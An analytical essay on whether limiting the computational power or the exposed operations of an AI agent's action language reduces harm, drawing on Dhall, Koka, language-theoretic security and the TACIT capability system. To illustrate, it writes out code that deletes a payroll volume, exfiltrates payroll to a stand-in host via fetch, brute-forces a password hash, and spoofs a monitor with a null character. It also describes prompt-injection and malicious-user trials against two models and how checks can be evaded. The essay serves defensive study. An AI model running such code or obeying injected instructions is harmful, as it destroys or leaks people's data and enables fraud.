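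The guide also recommends leaving out any argument that the application already knows. If the customer has selected an order, the model should be able to call `submit_refund()` without an order number. This is good advice because it stops the model from refunding the wrong order. It also reduces the tool's language to a single string, about as simple as a language can be, but the model can still pay out money by producing that string.

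A grammar can make an action language safer by excluding dangerous calls. Suppose the office assistant's grammar accepts two deletions:

```
delete_volume("staging")
delete_volume("backups")
```

Removing the second line protects the backups, but the language stays at the bottom level of the hierarchy because every finite set of strings is regular. If the designer then allowed any number of matching brackets around the remaining call, the language would rise to the context-free level without becoming any more dangerous.

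### Ranking agents by their memory

People also use the hierarchy more loosely, to rank machines by how much they can compute. *Computability of Agentic Systems* (Viriyasuthee, 2026) applies this ranking to AI agents whose models can read only a limited amount of text at once. On its own, such a model is equivalent to a finite-state machine. ReAct, a common design in which the model alternates between reasoning and using tools, is equivalent to a type of pushdown automaton. Agents that can look up their own earlier steps can be Turing-complete.

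Viriyasuthee is concerned with efficiency. For a task with *N* interdependent parts, the time grows as 2<sup>*N*</sup> for the pushdown designs but only as *N*<sup>2</sup> log *N* for an agent with the right kind of lookup. A faster agent could do more harm or more useful work in the same time, and the ranking doesn't distinguish between the two.

*Are Agents Probabilistic Automata?* (Koohestani, Li and colleagues, 2025) compares three designs for an agent that books flights. The simplest fills in a fixed set of details, such as the destination, date and budget. Another keeps a stack of unfinished tasks, so it can pause a booking to check the user's calendar. The most powerful can keep unlimited notes and reread any of them. All three call the same tools, including `search_flights` and `book`.

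The choice of design affects what a checker can establish. Given a model of how the tools and the language model behave, standard software can calculate a limit on the probability that the simplest agent calls `book` without the user's confirmation. No general method can answer such questions about the agent with unlimited notes unless the designer limits the run or simplifies the model of the agent. Koohestani and colleagues note that even the simplest design is not safe by construction. Any of the three agents could buy an expensive ticket to the wrong city with one call, and the researchers deliberately left what the tools can do out of their classification.

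The two papers also classify ReAct differently. Viriyasuthee places it at the pushdown level, while Koohestani and colleagues call it regular if its notes are limited and Turing-complete if it can accumulate and reread them without limit. An agent's level in the hierarchy depends partly on which parts of its memory the analyst counts.

### The Rule of Least Power

*The Rule of Least Power* (Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn, 2006), published by the World Wide Web Consortium, makes the classic argument for preferring weak languages. It advises publishers to choose the least powerful language that suits the purpose. If a weather service publishes its data in a simple format, any program can extract the temperatures, plot them or average them. If the service puts the data inside a Java program, a search engine may have to run the program to discover that it concerns the weather.

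They argue that weaker languages are "usually easier to secure" because security problems are easier to find in programs that are easier to analyse. Work on *language-theoretic security* extends this reasoning to programs' input formats.

Another of their examples is less convincing as evidence about computational power. They note that a bug-free processor for regular expressions avoids many of the security problems of a general system for running C++. That is true, but a regular expression can only report whether text matches, while a C++ program can usually also open files and contact other computers. The comparison therefore can't separate the effect of weaker computation from the effect of having fewer primitives.

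Robie (2006) made a similar objection on the W3C's mailing list. He shared the goals of simplicity, predictability and security, but thought that some weak languages just happened to have these qualities. He wrote that other languages offer little power and are still complex, unpredictable and dangerous.

Separating power from primitives gives four cases:

| | No dangerous primitive | A dangerous primitive |
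|---|---|---|
| Two-word language | "wait" and "beep": can make a noise | "wait" and "delete everything": can destroy all the data with one command |
| Turing-complete language with a step budget | No primitives at all: can use up its allowance of time and memory | `delete_volume`: can destroy any disk that the permissions allow |

The language consisting of "wait" and "delete everything" is finite, and a checker can analyse it completely by reading two lines. One of its two programs is a catastrophe. The Turing-complete language with no primitives can play chess against itself or compute the digits of pi until its budget runs out, without changing anything outside the interpreter. (If the host passes its answer to a person or another program, that is a disclosure, and the designer should count it as an effect.)

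So a language's power does not determine how dangerous it is. But these examples compare languages with different primitives. If two languages have the same primitives, the more powerful one might still be able to do more harm.

### The trace argument

Suppose the office has several disk volumes, each with a text file listing what is on it. The assistant has a Turing-complete language and writes this:

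```
n = 1
while "payroll" not in read_file("volume_" + str(n) + ".txt"):
    n = n + 1
delete_volume("volume_" + str(n))
```

The program reads the lists in turn until it finds the payroll, then erases that volume. A total language would reject its open-ended loop. But suppose the payroll is on volume 3. The program's *trace*, meaning the sequence of calls it makes together with their arguments, is then:

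```
read_file("volume_1.txt")
read_file("volume_2.txt")
read_file("volume_3.txt")
delete_volume("volume_3")
```

This trace is a program with no loops, variables or conditions, so a total language with the same primitives will accept it, and running it will destroy the same volume. The first three lines don't change anything, so the last line alone would do the same damage.

The same construction works for any program whose primitives are deterministic, meaning that the same call in the same state always has the same effect and returns the same reply. The starting state, *s*<sub>0</sub>, must also be known, and only the program's calls may change the state.

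1. Let a program make the calls *c*<sub>1</sub>, *c*<sub>2</sub> and so on, and let one of them cause harm. Harm here means the violation of a safety property, so it occurs after some finite number of calls, *n*.
2. Write out *c*<sub>1</sub> to *c*<sub>*n*</sub> in order, with the arguments that each call had. This gives a finite program without loops.
3. Start both programs in *s*<sub>0</sub>. If they are in the same state before a call, they make the same call and reach the same state after it. Since they start in the same state, they are in the same state after all *n* calls, and the loop-free program has done the same harm.

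Conversely, a Turing-complete language can also express a plain list of calls. So if program length is unlimited, programs in two languages with the same primitives can cause the same harms, even if one language is Turing-complete and the other can only list calls. The argument doesn't cover harm from the computation itself, such as tying up a processor, because that leaves no calls in the trace.

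This goes further than the theorem about bounded loops, which still requires loops to simulate a Turing machine on every input. Reproducing a single run from a known state requires no loops, because the outcome of every branch is already fixed.

### Programs that react to replies

A fixed list deletes the right volume only if its author knows where the payroll is. Without that knowledge, the program has to react to what it reads. If there are three volumes, it can do this with conditions alone:

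```
if "payroll" in read_file("volume_1.txt"):
    delete_volume("volume_1")
elif "payroll" in read_file("volume_2.txt"):
    delete_volume("volume_2")
elif "payroll" in read_file("volume_3.txt"):
    delete_volume("volume_3")
```

This program finds the payroll on whichever volume holds it, as the `while` loop did. It is longer, and with a thousand volumes it would need a thousand branches.

In general, such a program forms a tree. It starts with one call, has a branch for each possible reply, and makes the next call on each branch. If every call has at most *k* possible replies and the harm occurs within *n* calls, the tree contains at most

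1 + *k* + *k*<sup>2</sup> + … + *k*<sup>*n*−1</sup>

calls. With two replies per call, ten calls need a tree of at most 1,023, while forty need up to 1.1 trillion. If a reply can be any file of 1,000 characters, at eight bits per character, *k* alone is more than 10<sup>2,400</sup>. The tree is still finite, so the argument still holds in principle, although nobody could store the program.

A finite-state machine can carry out such a tree, using one state for each point in the tree. *Realizability for finite state reactive agents*, a LessWrong post, proves that such a machine can produce a deterministic behaviour exactly when the behaviour gives one output for each input, its earlier outputs do not depend on later inputs, and it needs only finite memory. A finite tree of calls meets these conditions if the machine waits after its last call. Finite-state machines, which are at the bottom of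 the hierarchy, can therefore do any harm that takes a limited number of calls with a limited range of replies.

### What the argument assumes

The trace argument compares which harms are possible, not how easy or likely they are. It rests on these assumptions:

- **Unlimited length.** The interpreter must accept the written-out program, however long it is. A limit of 100 lines would allow the four-line list above but not a tree that covers a thousand volumes.
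- **A known state.** If someone moves the payroll to volume 4 after the author has written the list, the list deletes the wrong volume, whereas the `while` loop still finds the right one. A tree can handle this uncertainty only if it has a branch for every reply that might come back.
- **A planner outside the language.** Something has to work out that the right argument is `"volume_3"`. If a harmful call needs a password, a one-line program with the correct password exists, but that is no help to an attacker who can't find it.

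If one of these assumptions fails, a language whose programs can search or react on their own may allow harm that a plain list of calls cannot.

An AI agent's planner is its language model. *Self-Programmed Execution for Language-Model Agents* (2026) defines the loop between model and interpreter mathematically, and allows the model to be any rule that assigns probabilities to its possible replies. This definition doesn't limit how cleverly the model chooses, so even an interpreter that accepts only one plain command at a time can receive its commands from a very capable planner.

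Such a planner doesn't need to write the whole tree. It can request `read_file("volume_1.txt")`, see that the payroll isn't there, and go on to the next volume. After reading volumes 2 and 3, it can request `delete_volume("volume_3")`. The assistant has then carried out the search from the `while` loop with four one-line programs, in an action language without loops or conditions.

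## When does computational power add to the danger?

If each of the model's turns takes two seconds, searching three volumes with one-line programs takes six seconds, but searching 3,000 takes an hour and forty minutes. A loop might search all 3,000 in seconds. The trace argument shows that a weak language and a powerful one can cause the same harms, but it does not address how long the harm takes or how much work it requires, and the best case for weak languages begins with those differences.

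### Sending 5,000 emails

Suppose the office has 5,000 contacts, and the assistant may email any of them. It reads a document with hidden instructions and writes this:

```
for contact in read_file("contacts.txt"):
    send_email(contact, "Please pay future invoices to our new account.")
```

The program is about 115 characters long. Without loops, the model would have to write 5,000 separate calls of about 80 characters each, or about 400,000 characters in total. Assume the model writes 400 characters a second, the mail server accepts 50 messages a second, and somebody stops the assistant ten minutes after the first message.

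| Action language | Delay before the first message | Time to send all 5,000 | Sent before someone steps in |
|---|---|---|---|
| Turing-complete, with `while` loops | Under a second | 100 seconds | 5,000 |
| Total, with `for` loops | Under a second | 100 seconds | 5,000 |
| A list of calls, with no loops | 17 minutes | 100 seconds | 5,000 |
| One call per turn, at two seconds a turn | Two seconds | 2 hours 47 minutes | 300 |
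| Any of these, with a cap of 50 calls | As above | Never sends them all | 50 |

Choosing a total language makes no difference, because it accepts the same loop. Removing loops delays the fraud by 17 minutes and produces an enormous program that a length limit would catch. Allowing one call per turn prevents most of the damage, but only because the interpreter has to wait for the model. Ten agents working at once could still send 3,000 messages in the same ten minutes.

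The cap works in all four languages. Like a step budget, it has to cover the whole task. It also has to count recipients as well as calls, because one call can reach a whole mailing list. The drawback is that a genuine newsletter to all 5,000 contacts would need somebody's approval.

Loops also let a program react faster than a person or a model can. Suppose the company's mail filter restarts every night and lets everything through for a tenth of a second. A program that tries to send the payroll a hundred times a second will succeed the first night. A model that tries once every two seconds will succeed about one night in twenty, unless it can find out when the filter restarts and time its attempt.

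A total language would permit this attack too. A loop with ten million passes is certain to end, but it would run for almost 28 hours at a hundred attempts a second. A cap that counted failed attempts would stop it after half a second.

### Combining two mild operations

Some harms need hardly any computation, only a way to pass the result of one call to another. Give the assistant a primitive called `fetch`, which downloads a web page:

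```
fetch("https://example.net/?note=" + read_file("payroll.txt"))
```

The assistant's job may include reading the payroll and looking things up on the web. But this line puts the payroll into the address it requests, so whoever runs `example.net` can read the payroll.

Removing the `+` so that programs can't join texts would achieve little if the model sees what `read_file` returns, since the model could copy the payroll into the address in its next program. A richer language can make the leak easier to catch. If the model writes the whole program before seeing any data, as Meijer proposes, a checker can follow the payroll from one call to the other, which it can't do once the text has passed through the model.

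More computation makes leaks easier to disguise. A program can scramble the payroll so that a filter looking for employees' names finds none. It can also leave the payroll out of the web addresses it requests and, for each bit, fetch one of two harmless pages, the first standing for a 0 and the second for a 1. A file of 1,000 characters, at eight bits each, would take 8,000 fetches, which is easy with a loop. If the program may make only 20 fetches, the choice of pages can reveal 20 bits, or two and a half characters.

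Dhall's designers had to deal with the same combination. A Dhall program can import files, web addresses and *environment variables*, which are named pieces of text that the operating system passes to programs and that often hold passwords or tokens. It can also attach extra information, called headers, to a web request. The tutorial for Dhall uses this to download from a private GitHub repository:

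```
[ { header = "Authorization", value = "token ${env:GITHUB_TOKEN as Text}" } ]
```

In this Dhall import, the user wants GitHub to receive the token. But if a downloaded package could also read the token and send it, the package's author could direct it to any server. Under Dhall's documented import rules, an import from the internet therefore may not refer to a local one. Dhall's test suite includes a remote file that tries to read an environment variable, which the interpreter must reject.

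This rule protects users from the packages they download. It would not protect an office from its own assistant, because a program the assistant writes on the office's machine is local. If the assistant can also save a small file containing the header, it can send the token anywhere. In the talk *Dhall*, Gonzalez (2020) mentions a simpler option, which is for the host to switch off web imports, or all imports.

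Imports also bring text in. The *Threat Model* for Pkl, another configuration language, lists web addresses, files and environment variables as sources of untrusted input. An AI agent faces the dangers of both untrusted input and leaked secrets, since a page it fetches may contain instructions that lead it to send out a secret.

### When the computation does the harm

The model can write out a list of calls or copy text from one program to the next, but it can't take over every computation. Suppose the assistant can read a file containing an administrator's password in *hashed* form, scrambled in a way that is easy to compute and practically impossible to reverse. To recover the password, a program has to scramble one guess after another and compare the results:

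```
stored = read_file("admin_hash.txt")
for n in range(26 ** 8):
    guess = letters(n)
    if scramble(guess) == stored:
        login("admin", guess)
```

There are 26<sup>8</sup>, or about 209 billion, possible passwords of eight lower-case letters. A program that makes ten million guesses a second can try all of them in under six hours. The number of passes through its loop is fixed at the start, so it can be written in a total language, where every program is guaranteed to terminate.

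The harmful part of the trace is one call to `login`, but nobody can write that call without first finding the password. Even at 33 guesses a second, a model would need about 200 years to write them all, and it would still have to scramble each one. An action language without loops therefore prevents this search, provided no primitive can run the search elsewhere.

A step budget also prevents the assistant from trying every possible password. If each guess takes a thousand steps, a budget of a billion steps allows a million guesses, enough to try one in 209,000 of the possible passwords. Neither restriction helps if the password is a common one that the model would try early, or if somebody has left it unscrambled where the assistant can read it, as in the experiment by Kaya and colleagues.

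Here a weaker machine does give a real guarantee, because a finite-state machine reads each character only once. More powerful programs can have a limit too. Parsers are programs that work out the structure of a text, and Vartanian writes in Increment that most tools for generating them produce code whose running time grows no faster than the cube of the input's length. For an input of 1,000 characters, that is something like a billion steps. Vartanian adds that most of these tools let developers insert their own code, which can break the limit. A primitive in an action language can also break it.

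Computation can also use up resources that somebody pays for, such as memory or calls to a language model. An attacker can profit from stolen processor time by mining cryptocurrency, but only if the program can send out its results.

### Listing every call in advance

The case for weak languages also rests on inspection. If a program is a plain list of calls, a checker can know exactly what it will request, in what order and with which arguments. Each addition to the language makes some of these answers less certain:

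| Question | A plain list of calls | With conditions, and replies as arguments | With a `for` loop over a file |
|---|---|---|---|
| How many emails can it send? | Exact number | An upper limit | Unknown until the checker knows the file's length |
| Can it call `delete_volume`? | Exact answer | "No" is reliable, but "yes" may be a false alarm | The same |
| Who will receive the emails? | Exact answer | Exact for addresses written in the program | Unknown until the checker reads the file |
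| Will the emails do any harm? | The list can't settle this | The list can't settle this | The list can't settle this |

False alarms arise because a program may contain a deletion in a branch that can never run. To rule out the deletion, a checker may have to determine whether any combination of replies could satisfy a complicated condition, and no known method is fast for every such condition.

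Even without loops, the upper limit can be high if the language has functions, because each function can call the previous one twice, like the doubling definitions in Dhall. Thirteen such functions are enough to email all the office's contacts.

If the host reads the contacts first, a Dhall program can loop over them and still give the checker an exact list, in this case 5,000 `send_email` entries. This works because all the reading happens before evaluation and all the sending after it. A Turing-complete language without side effects, run with a step budget, could produce the same list, or run out of steps and produce nothing.

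Totality does add something when part of the input is missing. This function uses `List/map`, a standard Dhall function that applies another function to every item in a list:

```
\(body : Text) ->
  List/map Text Action
    (\(name : Text) -> Action.send_email { to = name, body = body })
    [ "Ana", "Ben" ]
```

Dhall can simplify it before anyone supplies `body`:

```
\(body : Text) ->
  [ Action.send_email { to = "Ana", body = body }
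  , Action.send_email { to = "Ben", body = body }
  ]
```

A checker can now determine that only Ana and Ben will receive an email, whatever the email says. In a language with unrestricted recursion, this kind of simplification might never end.

Simplifying a program before checking it has limits. The Dhall tutorial notes that the interpreter can't simplify `Natural/even (n + n)` to `True`, although any natural number added to itself is even. A program that deletes the backups only when `n + n` is odd will never delete them, but the deletion remains in its simplified form, so a cautious checker would reject the program.

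Dhall can also detect changes to an imported program's meaning by checking a *hash*, a short fingerprint of the program's simplified form. Adding a comment or replacing `1` with `if True then 1 else 2` doesn't change the hash. If the program's result changes, the hash no longer matches and the interpreter rejects the import. An office could use this to approve a routine program once and still allow later edits that don't change its result.

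All these checks cover one program at a time. If an action language accepts only one call per turn, every program is trivial to list, but the list doesn't show which call the model will make next. The checker then needs a record of earlier calls, like the trace that Agent-C keeps. A longer program is harder to check but shows more of the plan in advance, so the shortest programs are not necessarily the easiest to supervise.

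### What language-theoretic security claims

Sassaman, Patterson and colleagues (2011) give a different argument for weak languages in *Security Applications of Formal Language Theory*. It concerns *parsing*, the step in which a program works out the structure of a file or message it has received. They treat the set of valid inputs as a formal language and the code that accepts or rejects inputs as a recogniser for that language.

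Many programs have no clear recogniser. Their checks are scattered through the code, and an attacker can look for an input that passes them but makes the program do something its developers never intended. In a buffer overflow, for instance, a program copies text into a space too small for it. The excess can overwrite the record of which instruction comes next, so the attacker's text determines what the program does. In effect, the input has become a program for a hidden computer that the developers built by accident, which security researchers call a *weird machine*.

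Sassaman and colleagues recommend making input formats as simple as their purpose allows and using parsers no more powerful than those formats need, under the slogan "Starve the Turing beast". They treat any added computational power in an input language as an extra privilege for whoever supplies the input. The LangSec project's website, *The Tower of Babel*, warns that if recognising valid input is undecidable, no amount of checking or testing will secure the program. This is true when the program accepts the full format, but a developer can instead accept a simpler subset and reject the rest, which is close to what the project recommends.

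They also want every component to read a message the same way. One of their examples involves the certificates that browsers use to verify a website's identity. An attacker who owned `badguy.com` could request a certificate for the name `www.paypal.com` followed by a null character (an invisible character with the code zero) and `.badguy.com`. The issuing authority read the whole name and saw that it belonged to the attacker's domain, but some browsers stopped at the null character and accepted the certificate as PayPal's.

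An action language can have the same weakness. Suppose a monitor allows emails only to addresses that end in `office.example`, and the assistant requests one to `eve@evil.example`, followed by a null character and `.office.example`. The monitor approves the request because the full address has the right ending. If the mail program stops reading at the null character, it sends the message to Eve. A simple address grammar that excludes null characters would prevent this, so the argument supports a simple *syntax* for action languages.

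Sassaman and colleagues' argument about parsing does not extend directly to the effects of actions. They deliberately set aside the question of what a receiver does with a message it has decoded correctly. In the PocketOS case, Railway's server decoded `volumeDelete` correctly and carried it out. An attack on a parser gives the attacker operations the designer never meant to offer, but a harmful action can use an operation the designer included on purpose.

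The paper's own database defence, Dejector, has the same limit. It takes a set of approved queries and builds a grammar that accepts only queries with the same structure. This stops an attacker from adding a second command to a query. But if one approved query deletes order 7, a query that deletes order 8 has the same structure, so the grammar accepts both, whichever order the customer wanted to cancel.

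### Why Dhall advertises that it is not Turing-complete

In *Why Dhall advertises the absence of Turing-completeness*, Gonzalez gives two reasons for mentioning that Dhall is not Turing-complete, even though this brings few safety guarantees by itself. One is that a language has to get several other things right before it can guarantee termination. The other is that the phrase "not Turing-complete" is a "shibboleth", a password by which people who dislike programmable configuration files recognise one another. Gonzalez writes that these people usually want files that have no arbitrary side effects, don't crash and don't hide what they do, and that none of this requires a total language. This reverses the view in the 2016 launch post on Haskell for All.

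matklad comes to much the same diagnosis but is less willing to keep the label. On this view, people want a configuration language to be deterministic, precisely defined, free of outside influences, secure and simple. Python fails the first test for a reason unrelated to loops: the expression `id([])` can give a different number each time someone starts Python. Keeping tokens away from an attacker is also a separate matter, which a designer handles by not giving programs general access to files and networks.

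Gonzalez's first reason works better for Dhall than for languages in general. Some side effects threaten termination. For example, a function that calls whatever a changeable memory cell contains will call itself forever if the program stores it in that cell. A total language has to rule this out, but it can still allow `delete_volume`. eBPF checks that programs terminate, yet it lets them reach thousands of kernel functions.

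One way to find out which of Dhall's guarantees depend on totality is to imagine two changes to the language:

| Guarantee | If Dhall allowed endless loops | If Dhall programs could call `delete_volume` |
|---|---|---|
| Evaluation always ends | Lost | Kept, as long as the call returns |
| Evaluating a program never deletes data | Kept | Lost |
| A program with fixed imports always gives the same result | Kept, for programs that end | Lost, if the reply depends on what is on the disk |
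| A downloaded package can't read local secrets | Kept, because of the import rule | Kept, because of the import rule |

Dhall's imports need separate rules for termination and secrecy. The interpreter rejects any file that imports itself, directly or through other files, but a hostile server can still keep the imports going by answering every request with code that imports a new address. The ban on remote code reading local data protects tokens but doesn't help with termination. Fetching a package also reveals to the server that somebody is using it. Dhall reduces this leak by keeping local copies of imports that have a fingerprint.

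Termination depends on the type checker. According to Dhall's release notes, version 1.19.0 fixed an error in the type rules that had made infinite loops possible. Even before the fix, Dhall programs couldn't send email, because the language had no operation for it.

Restrictions may also have a psychological benefit. matklad suggests, without much confidence, that banning recursion and open-ended loops could prompt people to look for a simpler solution. Vartanian similarly expects the limits to discourage people from using a small language for jobs it wasn't meant to do. Both effects depend on programmers finding roundabout code tedious to write. A language model can produce such code in seconds, so the restrictions probably discourage an AI agent less.

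In the 2020 talk, Gonzalez calls Dhall's purity, meaning its lack of side effects other than imports, the greatest single safeguard against malicious code. Gonzalez goes too far in concluding that Dhall can't compromise the host machine in any way, since doubling a short text forty times can exhaust the machine's memory. But Gonzalez also identifies the one remaining way Dhall can have an effect, which is through the program it configures. For the office assistant, that is the host program that sends the emails and deletes the volumes.

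## Can an action language be made safer by limiting what it exposes?

Whoever writes that host program also chooses which operations the assistant can reach. If the assistant's only job is to chase late timesheets, they could replace all three primitives with a single operation that sends a fixed reminder to a named employee. No program, in a total language or any other, could then use it to delete a volume. Security engineers call this *least privilege*, the rule that a program should have only the access its task requires. It goes back to a 1975 paper by Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder.

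Most software runs with more access than it needs. Miller (2006), in *Robust Composition*, gives the example of the card game Solitaire, which needs only a little memory and processor time, a window to draw in, and the player's clicks. But an ordinary operating system lets the game do almost anything the player could do, such as deleting the player's files.

### Passing a reference instead of a name

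These two Unix commands both copy a file:

```
cp timesheets.txt copy.txt
cat < timesheets.txt > copy.txt
```

In the first line, `cp` receives two file names. It has to open the files itself, which requires general permission to open files, so a faulty version could overwrite anything the user owns. In the second line, the command shell opens both files and passes `cat` the open connections, so `cat` could do this job without permission to open any file.

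An open connection of this kind is a *capability*, an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and permits its use. In an *object-capability* language, a program can affect the outside world only through such references. Miller lists four ways one component, Bob, can come to hold a reference to another, Carol. Bob may have had the reference from the start, Bob may have created Carol, Bob's creator may have built the reference in, or a component that already has references to both may pass Carol's to Bob. Bob can't get it by guessing Carol's name.

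Plain data works differently, because a program can get any number it can work out, "whether 7 or your private key", as Miller puts it. The Railway token was plain data because it was text that worked for anyone who read the file.

Capabilities also let a host hand over part of an operation. In this example, the host keeps `send_email` and gives the assistant only the function that `make_remind` returns:

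```
def make_remind(send_email, addresses):
    def remind(name):
        send_email(addresses[name], "Your timesheet is due on Friday.")
    return remind
```

`remind` is meant to let the assistant remind Ana without letting it change the message or write to an outsider. In Python, however, a program can use `remind`'s `__closure__` attribute to take `send_email` out. Object-capability languages have to rule out such workarounds. Miller excludes C++ because it can turn any number into a pointer, and standard Java because components can influence one another through shared global variables.

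Limiting what a language exposes doesn't require its programs to halt. Miller describes the object-capability model as essentially the untyped lambda calculus, with local memory and a restricted way of loading new code. A program in such a language may therefore loop forever, but it can't delete a volume it has no way to reach.

### Permission and authority

An assistant may be able to delete a volume it can't access directly. Suppose the office runs a clean-up service every night that deletes each volume named in a file called `unused.txt`. The assistant can't call `delete_volume`, but it can edit that file. If it adds the line "backups", the service will delete the backups the next time it runs.

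Miller would say that the assistant lacks *permission* to delete the volume but has the *authority* to do so. Permission is direct access, while authority covers everything a program can bring about, including what it can get other components to do. "Least privilege" could therefore mean either least permission or least authority, which can differ greatly. Miller defined both terms informally. *Permission and Authority Revisited* (Drossopoulou, Noble and colleagues, 2016) later proposed formal definitions using a small programming language.

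A list of current permissions is easy to check, but it would miss the clean-up service. An exact list of what the assistant could eventually cause usually can't be worked out, because it depends on how every other component behaves. In practice, an engineer can overestimate by drawing an arrow for every reference and assuming that each component will do the worst it can with the references it holds. If no path leads from the assistant to the backups, the assistant can't delete them. A path may indicate a real danger or be a false alarm.

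Knowing how some components behave makes the estimate more precise. `remind` holds a reference to `send_email`, but its code only sends one fixed text to addresses on one list. Someone who had only the diagram might conclude that the assistant could send any message to anyone.

Franco and Gershenson are less optimistic about this kind of analysis, citing a proof by Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman that no general method can determine whether a program will ever obtain a given access right. Miller thinks people often misread that proof. It shows that a designer can easily write rules for passing on rights that make the question undecidable, but at least three systems have rules that make it decidable. An office that designs its own action language can choose rules that keep the question decidable.

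Franco and Gershenson also show that agents which are safe on their own can be unsafe as a group. For example, one agent can read the payroll and write to a second agent, which can't read the payroll but can email people outside the company. Together they can send everyone's salary outside the company, though neither could do so alone. Franco and Gershenson cite an experiment in which combinations of language models produced vulnerable code in 43 per cent of trials, compared with 3 per cent for the models in isolation. Anyone checking the safety of an action language therefore also has to consider the other agents it lets an agent contact.

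### Recording effects in a function's type

A programming language can also record, before a function runs, what that function may do. In most languages, a function's *type* covers only its input and result, so a function that takes a number and returns a number might also print something or erase a disk. An *effect type* includes these other possible actions.

Leijen (2013), in *Koka*, describes a language built around this idea. A function that squares a number has the type `int → total int`, which promises that it has no side effects and always finishes. If a programmer adds a line that prints the number, the compiler works out the new type by itself:

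```
sqr : int → io int
```

Koka's other effects include `exn` for functions that may fail with an error, `ndet` for functions that may return different results for the same input, and `div` (short for "divergence") for functions that may never halt. Possible non-termination is thus one effect among several that a function might have.

*Koka* (2014), a later version of the paper, proves guarantees about the labels, including that evaluation terminates if a program's type lacks `div`. Koka's compiler leaves `div` off a function that calls itself if each call works on a smaller piece of data than the one before. It also checks for loops that go through a changeable memory cell, and it adds `div` when it can't tell whether a function terminates. This conservative approach was practical in a text-formatting program, where almost all functions were labelled `total` and only a handful had side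 effects.

Koka's `io` is too broad for the office assistant, since it covers printing a line and deleting a volume alike. It also includes `div`, so a type can't say that a function deletes something and then certainly stops. Leijen hoped to add finer effects later, including one for operations that can be reversed. With two invented effects, `mail` and `erase`, the assistant's functions might look like this:

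| What the function does | Effect |
|---|---|
| Adds up the hours on a timesheet | `total` |
| Searches for a counterexample to an unproved conjecture | `div` |
| Sends Ana one reminder | `mail` |
| Deletes one volume | `erase` |

A designer can ban `div` and `erase` independently. Banning `div` would reject only the search, and banning `erase` would reject only the deletion.

The same guarantees can cover code that a model writes while a program is running. *Language-Based Agent Control* extends a typed language with an operation that requests code of a given type from a model. It proves that programs using this operation keep every guarantee the type system gave ordinary programs. In outline, the proof replaces each request with the code the model returned, which leaves an ordinary program.

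### How TACIT keeps an agent from printing the payroll

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT, a system for AI agents that combines capabilities with types. The agents write their programs in a restricted version of the programming language Scala. This version is still Turing-complete, with unlimited loops and recursion.

An agent sends its code to a TACIT server, which passes it to the Scala compiler. If the compiler finds a violation, the server runs none of the code and returns the error message so that the agent can try again. Code that passes can reach files, the network and other programs only through TACIT's library. The library and the rest of the reusable code total about 1,000 lines.

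The compiler keeps track of which capabilities a value can use. It writes them in braces, as a *capture set*. Suppose `f` is a file and a function writes a given text to it. The function's type is

```
String ->{f} Unit
```

This means the function takes a text, returns nothing of interest (`Unit`), and may use `f`. A function of type `String -> Unit`, with no braces, can't use any capability. Odersky and colleagues call such a function *pure*.

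To open a file, a program requests a folder and does its work inside a block:

```
requestFileSystem("/office/timesheets") {
  access("late.txt").read()
}
```

The block receives a capability for that folder and returns the text of `late.txt`. The capability expires when the block ends. If the program returned a function that reads the file later, that function's capture set would have to include the folder's capability, which has no meaning outside the block, so the compiler would reject the program. The compiler can't check every file name in advance because a program may calculate one, so the library checks during the run that each path lies inside the folder. Programs request access to websites and external commands in the same way, by giving a list.

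Secrets have an additional protection. The administrator marks some folders as classified, and the library returns their contents in a wrapper called `Classified`. A program can't unwrap the text. It can only apply a function to it with `map`, which accepts pure functions and puts the result back in a wrapper. TACIT accepts this program:

```
requestFileSystem("/office") {
  val payroll = readClassified("/office/secret/payroll.txt")
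  val size = payroll.map(text => text.length)
  println(size)
}
```

The second line reads the payroll into a wrapper. The third applies a function that counts the characters. This function uses no file, network connection or screen, so it is pure and `map` accepts it. The last line prints the wrapped result, which appears as the number on the user's terminal, but the agent receives only `Classified(****)`.

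Now suppose the agent changes the third line and leaves out the last:

```
requestFileSystem("/office") {
  val payroll = readClassified("/office/secret/payroll.txt")
  payroll.map(text => println(text))
}
```

Printing requires an output capability. If that capability is called `io`, the function inside `map` has the type `String ->{io} Unit`, but `map` requires a function with an empty capture set. The compiler reports the mismatch, so the program never starts or reads the payroll.

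TACIT would accept a third version:

```
payroll.map(text => while true do ())
```

The loop runs forever, but it is pure in TACIT's sense because it uses no capability. A total language with the same operations but no capture sets would instead reject the loop and accept the program that prints the payroll.

These guarantees depend on closing loopholes like Python's `__closure__`, so TACIT bans agents from using *casts*, which make the compiler treat a value as if it had another type. With a cast, an agent could relabel the printing function as pure. It also bans *reflection*, which lets a program find and call functions by name while it runs.

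An agent may still need to work with a secret it can't see. TACIT lets it pass the wrapped text to a second language model, which the user trusts and runs locally. That model can summarise a confidential contract, for example, but its summary also comes back wrapped. The user can read the summary, but the company that hosts the agent's model receives neither the contract nor the summary.

### The same language with secrets wrapped and unwrapped

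Odersky and colleagues tested this protection on a sample software project with a folder of passwords, a database and confidential documents. They ran 131 trials each with Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5 in which the contents of the secret folder came in wrappers, and another 131 each in which they came as ordinary text.

Most of the trials paired a legitimate request with an attack hidden in the project's files. Combining 12 requests, such as listing the functions of a web application, with 10 attacks gave 120 trials. Some attacks told the agent that the secrets were only test data, while others contained ready-made Scala code for reading them. In the remaining 11 trials, the user was the attacker. Five of these users simply asked for the secrets, and six pretended to have a good reason, for instance by posing as an administrator in an emergency.

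The number of trials in which a secret appeared in the agent's output was as follows:

| Model and type of trial | Secrets as ordinary text | Secrets in wrappers |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, hidden attacks (120) | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, malicious users (11) | 2 | 0 |
| MiniMax M2.5, hidden attacks (120) | 3 | 0 |
| MiniMax M2.5, malicious users (11) | 8 | 0 |

The share of trials without a leak therefore rose from 98.5 to 100 per cent for Claude and from 91.6 to 100 per cent for MiniMax. The agents wrote in the same Turing-complete language under both conditions. Only the exposure of the secrets changed, so a difference in computational power can't explain the result.

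The improvement rests on few cases. Ten of the 13 leaks came from trials with malicious users, and each model had only 11 of those. Claude resisted every hidden attack without the wrapper, so there was nothing to improve there. Odersky and colleagues also built their own test, which measures the property their compiler enforces. The zeros in the last column are still more convincing than a sample of 131 would normally be, because the wrapper works the same way whether or not the model cooperates. The trials mainly confirm that the implementation has no obvious hole.

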